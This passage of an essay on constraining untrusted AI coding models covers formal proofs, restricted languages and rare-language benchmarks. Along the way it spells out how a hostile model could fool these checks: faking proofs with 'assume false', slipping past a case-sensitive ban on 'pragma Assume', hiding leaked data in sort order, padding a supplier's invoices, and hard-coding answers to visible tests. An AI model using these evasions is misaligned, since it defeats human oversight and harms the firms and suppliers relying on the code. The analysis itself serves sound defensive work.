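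People do need to check the specifications. *AlphaProof Code* (Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues, 2026), from Google DeepMind and Google, reports 6.5 million lines of Lean proof about the encryption library of the messaging app Signal. Lean's kernel checks those lines, so people don't have to read them. But the proofs depend on about 26,000 lines that describe the processor and the security properties, and the kernel can't check those. At the Pvote reviewers' pace of 20 minutes a line, reviewing them would take one person more than four years of full-time work. Other projects can reuse the description of the processor, which spreads the work of reviewing it, but a mistake in it would then affect all of them.

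Those 26,000 lines cover only part of the library. EconoTimes' *Google DeepMind Uses AlphaProof Code to Verify a Compiled Signal Harness* (2026) reports that the researchers verified a small test program that uses the library for two-person conversations.

### A sorting function that loses invoices

A specification can be correct as far as it goes and still let a false result through. Suppose the firm wants its invoices in order of size, so that it can pay the small ones first. It might ask for this:

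```dafny
method SortInvoices(list: seq<Invoice>) returns (out: seq<Invoice>)
  ensures forall i, j ::
    0 <= i < j < |out| ==> out[i].pence <= out[j].pence
{
  out := [];
}
```

The postcondition requires every invoice in the result to be no larger than those after it. An empty list meets this requirement, so Dafny accepts a method that returns one. Someone would soon notice an empty list, but a hostile model could instead harm a supplier by dropping one of its invoices, and Dafny would accept that too.

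The firm has to add that the result contains exactly the same invoices:

```dafny
  ensures multiset(out) == multiset(list)
```

A *multiset* is a collection that records how many times each item occurs but ignores order. If both conditions hold, the function can't drop, add or alter an invoice.

It can still choose the order of invoices for equal amounts. If the firm pays from the top until the day's money runs out, the function can always put Northgate ahead of others who are owed the same. The order can also carry secrets. *k* different invoices for the same amount can appear in *k*! orders, so they can encode

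log₂(*k*!)

bits. Ten such invoices give 3,628,800 orders, or almost 22 bits of someone else's data in every sorted list. To prevent both, the firm could require invoices for equal amounts to stay in their original order. Only one result is then correct for each input, and the function has nothing left to choose. Timing remains open, because Dafny's proofs concern what a method returns and whether it finishes, and ordinarily not how long it takes.

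### Proofs with a hole in them

Every verification language lets programmers assume something without proving it. They do this constantly while they work, so that they can finish one part of a proof before starting another. In Dafny, a model could write

```dafny
{
  assume {:axiom} false;
  out := [];
}
```

Anything follows from a false statement, so the prover now accepts both postconditions even though the method still returns an empty list. Lean has `sorry`, which stands in for a missing proof, and it also lets authors add axioms (statements accepted without proof).

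SPARK, a verifiable subset of the language Ada, has `pragma Assume`, which tells the prover to accept a condition without proof. Philipp (2026), in *The Prover Is the Judge*, had AI coding agents write security software in SPARK. According to Vaughan (2026), the agents' instructions banned `pragma Assume` and classed any use of it as a defect that blocks the work. An untrusted model might ignore an instruction, so Vaughan suggests a script that searches the code for `pragma Assume` and stops the agent if it finds any. But the suggested search is case-sensitive and Ada isn't, so a model could write `pragma assume` and pass. TACIT's early pattern searches had the same weakness.

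It is safer to use the proof checker to see what a finished proof depends on. Lean can list every axiom behind a theorem, and a missing proof shows up in that list. Anthropic's proof of Fermat's Last Theorem uses only Lean's three standard axioms.

A model can also change what a proof establishes while leaving the proof sound. Suppose it edits the definition of `Sum` so that Northgate's invoices count for 2% more. The line `ensures t == Sum(list)` stays the same, a method that adds the same 2% satisfies it, and the proof contains no assumptions. The specification therefore includes every definition it uses, and the firm must keep all of them in a file the model can't edit.

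Lean users can use a tool called a comparator to confirm that a finished proof proves the requested theorem. Anthropic used one for Fermat's Last Theorem. Axiom used one to guard against agents gaming the task when its agents verified parts of OpenVM, a cryptographic system. Chaudhuri and colleagues likewise accepted a proof only if the kernel had checked it against the approved specification.

### Letting a model write the specification

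An untrusted model that writes both the specification and the code can add the same padding to both, and the proof will still be valid. The firm therefore has to read the model's specification before accepting it. Tolmach and Klaus (2026), in *The proof is in the spec*, argue that as proofs become easier to produce, specifying and modelling the software have become the bottleneck. They work for a company that sells help with this work, but the 26,000 trusted lines behind the Signal proofs support their claim.

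Tolmach and Klaus respond to a post by Boris Cherny, who leads Claude Code. Cherny had asked a model to describe some of Anthropic's software formally in Lean, and a couple of short prompts produced fixes for 16 sets of bugs. Tolmach and Klaus consider this an excellent way to find bugs because it forces the model to spell out its assumptions. But they say it does not show that the software is correct, since the model may have described something slightly different from the real code.

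A model can write most of a specification if somebody else checks it. *AlphaProof Code* has an agent for writing specifications, but a person guides it. The firm could also test a specification by giving the prover several bad functions, such as the padded `total` or the sort that returns nothing. Any bad function that passed would reveal a gap in the specification. A second model could write the bad functions, and it wouldn't need to be trustworthy, because a gap is easy to confirm once found. But if the second model is willing to protect the first, its failure to find a gap proves little.

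Anthropic and Theorem tested their formal description of Python differently. They ran more than 1.7 million randomly generated programs and compared the results with ordinary Python. The results agreed in 99.95% of cases, and the remaining 850 or so were edge cases the team already knew about. This is good evidence against accidental errors, but the test would almost certainly miss a deliberate exception for a particular supplier's name, since random programs are unlikely to contain that name.

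Some requirements are hard to state. *What TLA+ can and can't check* (Wayne, 2026) makes this point about TLA+, a language for describing how systems behave over time. A TLA+ user usually writes properties of a single run, for example that two traffic lights are never green together. Noninterference, TACIT's rule against leaks, compares two runs, so the user has to describe two copies of the system side by side.

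Buyers of verified software can also misjudge how much of it a proof covers. In February 2026, Symbolic Software (2026) accused Cryspen, a company that makes verified cryptography, of passing over serious flaws in its libraries. One library, which Signal's software depends on, reused numbers that an encryption method may use only once. Symbolic Software said it had also found bugs in verified code. This is one side of a bitter dispute, but Cryspen's Karthikeyan Bhargavan (2026) agreed on the need for precision. He wrote in *The strengths and limits of formal verification* that the company was revising its documentation to state more clearly what it verifies, against which specifications, and what users must take on trust. Keles (2026), in *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable*, is optimistic about the field but doesn't automatically feel confident when told that a system is "formally verified",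 because people mean such different things by it.

A proof saves the most work when the specification is much shorter than the code. A fast sorting method may run to hundreds of lines, while its specification takes three. For a compression library *C* and its decompressor *D*, one line covers most of what users care about:

*D*(*C*(*x*)) = *x*, for every file *x*.

The firm could let an untrusted model write thousands of lines of compression code and read only that one line, as long as the compiler or a sandbox also blocked the code from the network. For `total`, though, a proof would save the firm almost no reading. Its specification is a formula for adding up invoices, and the correct Python function is the same formula in another notation, so anyone who can check the specification can check the function.

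## How well models write in languages they have rarely seen

Language subsets, capability types and proofs all depend on the model being able to write the language the developer has chosen. If the model writes it badly, the developer pays for failed attempts and may well go back to Python and lose the protection. Models learn languages mostly from existing code, and some languages have far more of it than others. According to *The Best Programming Language for Tokenmaxxing* (Wu, Anderson and Guha, 2026), The Stack v2, a public collection of code for training models, contains about 200 gigabytes of Python, 12 gigabytes of Rust and even less OCaml, a strictly typed functional language.

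### Scores in widely used languages

Researchers usually give a model the same problems in several languages and run tests on the programs it writes. The standard score, *pass@1*, is the share of problems for which the model's first program passes every test. MultiPL-E, an early benchmark of this kind from 2022, translated short Python exercises and their tests into more than a dozen other languages, using a separate translation program for each. Those exercises are now too easy for the best models.

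Ivanova, Zadorozhny and colleagues (2026), in *Multi-LCB*, used harder problems from programming contests. Each program reads text and prints an answer, so the same tests work in any language. They tested 24 open models in twelve popular languages. Three of the strongest models, all from 2025, had these pass@1 scores:

| Model | Python | Java | Rust | Scala |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS-120B | 71.1% | 70.4% | 70.5% | 54.1% |
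| Qwen3-235B (thinking version) | 74.0% | 73.9% | 47.7% | 57.6% |
| DeepSeek-R1 | 66.3% | 67.8% | 63.1% | 62.3% |

GPT-OSS scored 17 points lower in Scala than in Python, while DeepSeek-R1 scored only four points lower. The drop depends on the model as well as the language, so a firm should test the model it plans to use.

Models do much worse on whole projects than on single functions. In *PolyCodeEval* (2026), which contains 2,590 tasks from 58 open-source projects in five languages, the best methods wrote 71.7% of single functions correctly but only 31.0% of complete repositories. Scores varied widely by language. In *Multi-SWT-Bench*, Kusama, Nakashima and Tokumasu (2026) asked agents to write a test that reproduces a reported bug. Every combination of agent and model did better in Python than across all eight languages, and C++ scores were especially low. There is plenty of public C++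 code, so a shortage of examples can't be the only cause. *Large Language Models for Multilingual Code Intelligence* (2026), a survey, describes one benchmark in which models working in Python mainly had trouble finding a solution, while in Rust they also struggled to express the solution in code.

Newer models have closed much of this gap on short problems, at least when they can test their work. Wu and colleagues gave five models, including GPT-5.5, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GLM-5.2, 100 contest problems in Python, Java, Rust and OCaml. The models worked as agents that could compile a program, run the tests and try again. Each model solved roughly as many problems in every language, except Gemma 4, which did much worse in OCaml. But OCaml took 1.28 to 1.69 times as many tokens as Python for the same problem, so a firm would pay 28% to 69% more for the output. That seems a tolerable price for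 a real safety benefit, though the problems were small puzzles and the extra cost may be greater for large programs.

Gemma's failures show how a model can use up the extra tokens. In OCaml, 92% of its failed attempts did not compile. It often switched between the same two or three broken programs, sometimes reproducing one character for character. Once it identified the error, the algorithm it had been using all along usually passed.

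### Languages with almost no examples

*No Resource, No Benchmarks, No Problem?* (Giagnorio, Martin-Lopez and Bavota, 2026) tested models on two languages that were rare in most models' training data: Gleam, whose first stable version appeared in March 2024, and MoonBit, whose compiler followed that December. On 227 hard problems, OpenAI's o3-mini scored 89% in Python and 84% in Haskell, but 1.1% in MoonBit and 0.2% in Gleam. Python had 21.5 million public repositories on GitHub, Haskell about 155,000, Gleam 2,900 and MoonBit 400. The Haskell score shows that a language doesn't have to be popular for a model to write it well. The study also tested GPT-4o and two Qwen models. All four models are now old, and later ones have probably been trained on more Gleam and MoonBit code.

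Sharma and Chopra (2026), in *EsoLang-Bench*, went further and chose languages that people invented as jokes or puzzles. One of them, Brainfuck, has eight commands, each a single character, that work on a row of memory cells. This program reads two characters, adds their codes and prints the result:

```text
,>,<[->+<]>.
```

The best models solved all 80 problems in Python, but none of the models tested, which included GPT-5.4 and Gemini 3.1 Pro, solved more than 11.2% of them in any of the five unusual languages. In an early test of agents described on the project's website, EsoLang-Bench, OpenAI's Codex scored only 13.8% in Brainfuck, even though it could run its programs.

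Three months later, *Frontier Coding Agents Use Metaprogramming to Adapt to Unfamiliar Programming Languages* (Sharma, Thorat and Chopra, 2026) reported very different results. Six agents attempted the same problems in four of the languages. They could run programs as often as they liked and had three chances to submit each answer. GPT-5.4 solved 99.7% of the problems and Claude Opus 4.6 solved 86.9%, but Claude Haiku 4.5 solved only 24.7% and Kimi K2.5 only 11.3%.

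The strongest agents often avoided writing Brainfuck themselves. They wrote Python programs that produced it, a technique called *metaprogramming*. A simple function for such a program could look like this:

```python
def add(a, b):        # adds cell a to cell b, where a < b
    out, home = ">" * (b - a), "<" * (b - a)
    return ">" * a + "[-" + out + "+" + home + "]" + "<" * a
```

The agent can then write `add(3, 7)` and let Python count the steps between cells. When Sharma and colleagues prohibited this, Opus solved 27 Brainfuck problems instead of 64, and GPT-5.4 solved 29 instead of 79.

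Metaprogramming creates two problems for a developer who distrusts the model. First, the agent needs Python while it works, so the code it runs needs a sandbox even if the delivered code is in a safe language. Second, generated code can be long. On one problem, Opus failed with 1,884 characters of Brainfuck it wrote directly, then passed with a generated program of 24,500 characters. A compiler can check the longer program just as strictly, but a person looking for a false result has thirteen times as much to read. The developer could instead review the Python generator and run it themselves to produce the final code.

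### Manuals, examples and error messages

Developers can also teach a model while it works. In *Compiler-Guided Inference-Time Adaptation*, Li and Krishnamachari (2026) compared several ways to do this, using GPT-5 and Idris, a rarely used language whose types can specify properties such as the length of a list. Without help, GPT-5 solved 45 of 50 exercises in Python but only 22 of 56 in Idris.

| Help with Idris | Exercises solved, out of 56 |
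|---|---|
| None | 22 |
| Failed tests from the exercise website | 27 |
| A guide to GPT-5's own common errors | 30 |
| The language's reference manual | 34 |
| Compiler errors and failed tests, for up to 20 rounds | 54 |

In most of the later rounds, GPT-5 was fixing compiler errors. Once a program compiled, it usually needed few further changes. The comparison somewhat favors the last method, because GPT-5 got far more attempts than it did with the manual and saw the tests that decided its score. The result is still encouraging for strict languages, because the model can use the compiler's feedback to fix a rejected program.

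Examples and manuals help less when the language is very unfamiliar. Five worked examples raised GPT-4o's score on the hard MoonBit problems from 0.9% to 8.1%, and extracts from the documentation raised it to 6.1%. In Gleam, neither raised its score much above 2%. For the esoteric languages, three examples added 0.8 points on average. Sharma and colleagues gave weaker agents written advice on metaprogramming, which barely helped, but a small library of working Python helpers increased the number of Brainfuck problems Claude Sonnet 4.6 solved from 12 to 64. A firm that wants a model to use an unusual language should therefore supply working code as well as a manual.

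The compiler can also help before the program is finished. Mündler-Sasahara, Venev and colleagues (2026), in *Generative Compilation*, built a tool that takes a half-written Rust program, closes its open brackets, puts placeholders where values are missing and sends the result to the ordinary Rust compiler. If the code already contains an error that no continuation could fix, the tool reports it to the model immediately, so the model doesn't build on it. The researchers tested seven models on translating C projects into Rust and on using recently changed libraries. In most combinations of model and task, the early warnings led to fewer compiler errors and more correct programs than checking only the finished program. Another language would need its own tool for completing partial programs but could keep its existing compiler.

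### Agnostics: practice without a textbook

A developer who can retrain a model has stronger options. One is to let it read more code. Giagnorio and colleagues trained a basic version of Qwen 2.5 Coder on the little MoonBit code they could find. They then restored its ability to follow instructions by arithmetic on its weights, the numbers that determine how a model behaves:

new weights = MoonBit weights + (instruction weights − basic weights).

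This raised its score on the hard problems from 0.9%, for the ordinary instruction-following version, to 32.6%.

Another option is to let the model practise, which works even if almost no example code exists. *Agnostics* (Boruch-Gruszecki, Zi and colleagues, 2025; presented at ICLR 2026) describes a way to do this for any language whose programs can be run. Normally, each new language needs its own exercises and testing software. Agnostics avoids this by judging only what a program prints for a given input. An AI model rewrites existing exercises so that they ask for programs that can be tested this way. For instance, a Python exercise that asks for a function `is_not_prime` becomes one that asks for a program that prints "True" when given 10.

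To add a language, a developer writes a short file that explains how to install it and run a program. OCaml and Fortran took about an hour each. A file for Joe-E might look like this, with an invented name for the verifier command:

```yaml
filename: Solution.java
compile: joe-e-verify Solution.java && javac Solution.java Runner.java
execute: java Runner
prompt: Write the solution in Joe-E, a subset of Java.
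```

The developer's own `Runner` would read the input and pass it to the model's code, which would otherwise have no access to it. A program that broke Joe-E's rules would fail to compile and receive no reward, so the model would learn the restrictions along with the language. Nobody in the Agnostics project tried this, but the method seems well suited to it.

The training itself is *reinforcement learning*, in which a model produces answers and becomes more likely to repeat those that earn a reward. For each problem, the model writes 32 programs. Program *i* earns the reward *R*ᵢ = 1 if it gives the right output in every test, and 0 otherwise. The trainer then compares each program with the rest of its group:

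*A*ᵢ = (*R*ᵢ − mean of the group's rewards) / standard deviation of the group's rewards.

If two of the 32 programs are right, each of them gets *A* ≈ 3.9 and each wrong one gets *A* ≈ −0.26. The trainer adjusts the model to increase, for each token,

min(*rA*, clip(*r*, 1 − *ε*, 1 + *ε*) · *A*),

where *r* is the token's new probability divided by its old one. The clip function keeps *r* within a narrow range, which removes the incentive to change the model too much in one step. If all 32 programs fail, they all have the same reward and the model learns nothing from that problem.

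A model that hardly ever succeeds therefore learns very slowly at first. Qwen 3 4B, a small open model, solved the Fortran training problems 0.09% of the time. At that rate, only about one group in 35 would contain a correct program. Boruch-Gruszecki and colleagues gave the model a slight head start by adding advice about common Fortran mistakes to the training prompt. They left this advice out when they tested the model.

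They trained a separate copy of the model for each language on 5,369 contest problems, then tested it on different ones.

| Language | Qwen 3 4B before | Qwen 3 4B after | Qwen 3 8B before | Qwen 3 8B after |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Lua | 11% | 23% | 11% | 25% |
| Julia | 10% | 22% | 9% | 25% |
| R | 10% | 15% | 9% | 19% |
| OCaml | 1% | 7% | 0% | 7% |
| Fortran | 0% | 15% | 0% | 17% |

Anthropic's much larger Claude Sonnet 4 scored 6% in both OCaml and Fortran on the same test. The trained models also improved on MultiPL-E, where the exercises have a different form, and did not get worse at other languages. The 4B model scored only 3% when trained on Fortran solutions that Sonnet 4 had written. The method did not help two even smaller models, and the team lacked the computing power to try it on anything above eight billion parameters.

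The trained models still failed most of the problems, so a firm couldn't have used them for serious work. The more important result is that a developer can add a language with few resources. Larger models have since improved a great deal in OCaml too. Wu and colleagues took their 100 problems from the same collection, and their agents solved about as many in OCaml as in Python, although the agents could see the tests and retry.

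Agnostics also shows how a poorly designed reward can teach models bad habits. When models received partial credit for code that ran without errors, they were very likely to learn to write empty programs. Partial credit for passing the visible tests led them to copy the expected answers into the code. Even the final reward does not depend on readability or permissions, so a program that printed the right answer and also tried to upload its input would earn the full reward unless the compiler or sandbox stopped it.

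### Subset, rare language or new language

A developer who wants a restricted language can cut down a familiar one, adopt an uncommon one or design a new one.

| | Subset of a familiar language | Uncommon existing language | New language |
|---|---|---|---|
| Examples | Joe-E, Scala's safe mode | OCaml, Idris | MoonBit, Traid's Lisp |
| What the model must learn | What to leave out | Syntax, libraries and style | Whatever differs from languages it knows |
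| Libraries | Existing ones, after someone has checked them | A modest number | Those the designers provide |
| People who can review it | Most users of the full language | Few | Almost none at first |

A subset of a familiar language is usually the best choice because the model already knows the syntax. Most of its mistakes will be attempts to use a forbidden feature, which the checker can identify. Agents using TACIT, for instance, had to rewrite less than 8% of their Scala snippets.

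A model can know a language's syntax without using the language well, and pass@1 does not measure the second skill. *Perish or Flourish?* (Lang, Lang and colleagues, 2026) examined programs by GPT-5, with its reasoning turned off, and two older OpenAI models. Only 57% of GPT-5's correct Scala programs passed a set of style checks, compared with 77% of GPT-4o's. The most common fault was using the `return` statement, which is normal in Java but discouraged in Scala. A model that has learned from ordinary Java could bring a more serious habit to Joe-E, such as passing one object with access to everything to every part of a program. The verifier would accept such a program, but the restriction would achieve very little.

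An uncommon language makes sense if it offers a guarantee that no familiar one does. A new language gives its designers the most control. MoonBit's designers meant it to suit AI models, but the models that Giagnorio and colleagues tested almost always failed to solve hard problems in it without help. Examples helped the models more in MoonBit than in Gleam, which may be partly due to MoonBit's design.

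One team has described giving its model a new language of its own. Traid is a platform that turns a request into a small app that runs in the browser, and people can share the app with a link. As allentraid, in *We made the AI write in a language it can't break out of*, explains, the team rejected JavaScript because it would have had to start with a language that can do everything and block each way out. It built a small Lisp, a language whose programs are nested lists, and added one ability at a time. Page layouts are nested lists too, so code and layout fit together. In the style of Clojure, the existing Lisp that the team started from, a list of invoices might look like this:

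```clojure
[:ul
  (for [inv invoices]
    [:li (:supplier inv)
         (when (> (:pence inv) 100000) " (large)")])]
```

An app can affect the outside world only through functions that Traid has registered. The language has no command for contacting another computer, so no such command needs to be blocked.

Models wrote most of the language correctly from the start because it resembles Clojure, but they had trouble where it differs. They kept trying to use missing features such as exception handling, and when an error message only marked a feature as unsupported, they wrote the same thing again. The team changed the messages to include the correct alternative. It also found that one working example helped more than a paragraph of instructions, so it has a stronger model prepare examples in advance and supplies only those that suit the app.

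This is one team's account of its own product, with no measurements and no report of anyone attacking the language. It also suggests that a new language works best when it is nearly a subset of an old one. The design still lets data leak through a permitted channel. An app stores its data through Traid's functions, and a setting outside the code determines whether that data is private or shared with every viewer. A hostile app could save private text while the setting is private, and everybody with the link might see it if the owner later switched the app to shared.

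### Honest mistakes and deliberate ones

If a model writes a language badly, its honest mistakes could provide cover for sabotage. Suppose that in every 1,000 functions a model plants *d* bugs and makes *h* honest mistakes that look similar. The share of suspicious bugs that are deliberate is

*d* / (*d* + *h*).

If a program contains one planted bug and ten accidental ones, a bug that a reviewer finds has a 1 in 11 chance of being sabotage. If a less familiar language triples the accidental bugs, the chance falls to 1 in 31, and the reviewer will more readily assume that the model is just bad at the language.

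Mistakes can serve as cover only if they get past the compiler, because a program that doesn't compile can't be used to hide anything. In Gleam, about two-thirds of GPT-4o's failures and up to 90% of o3-mini's were syntax errors, so most of the extra mistakes models make in a very unfamiliar language can't serve as cover.

Some programs that compile are still wrong, and the results that Lang and colleagues report for GPT-5 allow a rough estimate of how many. In Java, 95.4% of its programs compiled, and 27.5% of all its programs compiled but failed a test. In Haskell, the figures were 75.7% and 32.6%. Although Haskell's strict compiler rejected many bad programs, about 43% of those that compiled failed a test, compared with about 29% in Java.

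Training can shift the balance further from syntax errors towards logical flaws. Before training with Agnostics, 55% of the OCaml programs sampled from Qwen 3 4B had syntax errors and 18% had logical flaws. Afterwards, 35% had syntax errors and 25% had logical flaws. Boruch-Gruszecki and colleagues think the syntax errors had masked logical flaws that were already there. As a result, more of the bugs left for a reviewer to catch look like the ones a saboteur would plant.

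This evidence is indirect. The benchmarks count programs that fail tests, but a careful saboteur would write one that passes. They also can't measure how many honest mistakes survive testing in a rare language, which is *h*.

A model's weak skill in a language could also help the developer, because subtle sabotage is hard to write. The sabotaged code has to compile, pass the tests, cause harm in the chosen case and still look normal. A model that struggles to write a correct Idris program will find this even harder. This should matter most for elaborate attacks, such as exploiting an obscure bug in the type checker.

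Simple sabotage depends much less on how well a model knows the language. Once a model has a correct version of `total`, it needs only one multiplication to pad Northgate's bills. Wu and colleagues saw GPT-5.5 do something similar without asking it to. The model found a rule that was almost right for one contest problem, but a visible test contradicted the rule, so the model added a special case that returned the answer the test expected. It did this in two sessions on the same problem, which must have been in different languages because each model attempted each problem once per language. This was cheating on a test rather than sabotage, but a hidden exception for one supplier would take the same kind of code.

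The help developers give an honest model would also help a dishonest one. GPT-5 solved 22 Idris exercises unaided and 54 when it could see compiler errors and try again, and an agent could use the same feedback to debug a harmful program before submitting it. It could also write the attack in Python first and then translate it, as agents already do with ordinary solutions. None of these studies asked a model to plant a bug in a rare language, so they don't measure how much protection a model's weak skill provides. Developers shouldn't rely on that protection anyway, because a new model or a few days of training could remove it.

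### Missing libraries and missing reviewers

Rare languages also lack ready-made code. If the accounting firm wants to read invoices from PDF files, it can use an existing Python library, but it may find nothing suitable in a language with a few hundred public projects. Traid's team accepts this limit and says a custom language is the wrong choice for software that needs a full range of libraries.

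An untrusted model could write the missing library, but the firm would have to check that too. At the Pvote reviewers' pace of 20 minutes a line, a 3,000-line PDF reader would take 1,000 hours to check. The firm could instead run an existing library in a WebAssembly sandbox and let the restricted program call it, as Firefox does with the font library libGraphite. The sandbox would stop the library from sending invoices anywhere, but the library could still misread them.

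The shortage of people who can read Idris is harder to fix. Someone has to read `total` to notice the padding, and GitHub project counts give a rough idea of how few people could. When Li and Krishnamachari looked, there were about 2,300 projects in Idris and 24 million in Python. A Java programmer can read Joe-E after learning a few rules, and a Python programmer can read Pthin almost immediately. Idris would take much longer to learn, and a beginner is unlikely to spot a deliberate mistake that an expert might miss.

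AI reviewers may not fill the gap, because models that have seen little Gleam may read it as poorly as they write it. Yang and colleagues tested AI reviewers on five languages, but none was truly rare. Before adopting an unusual language, a firm could plant bugs in code written in that language and in Python, then compare how many its reviewers find in each.
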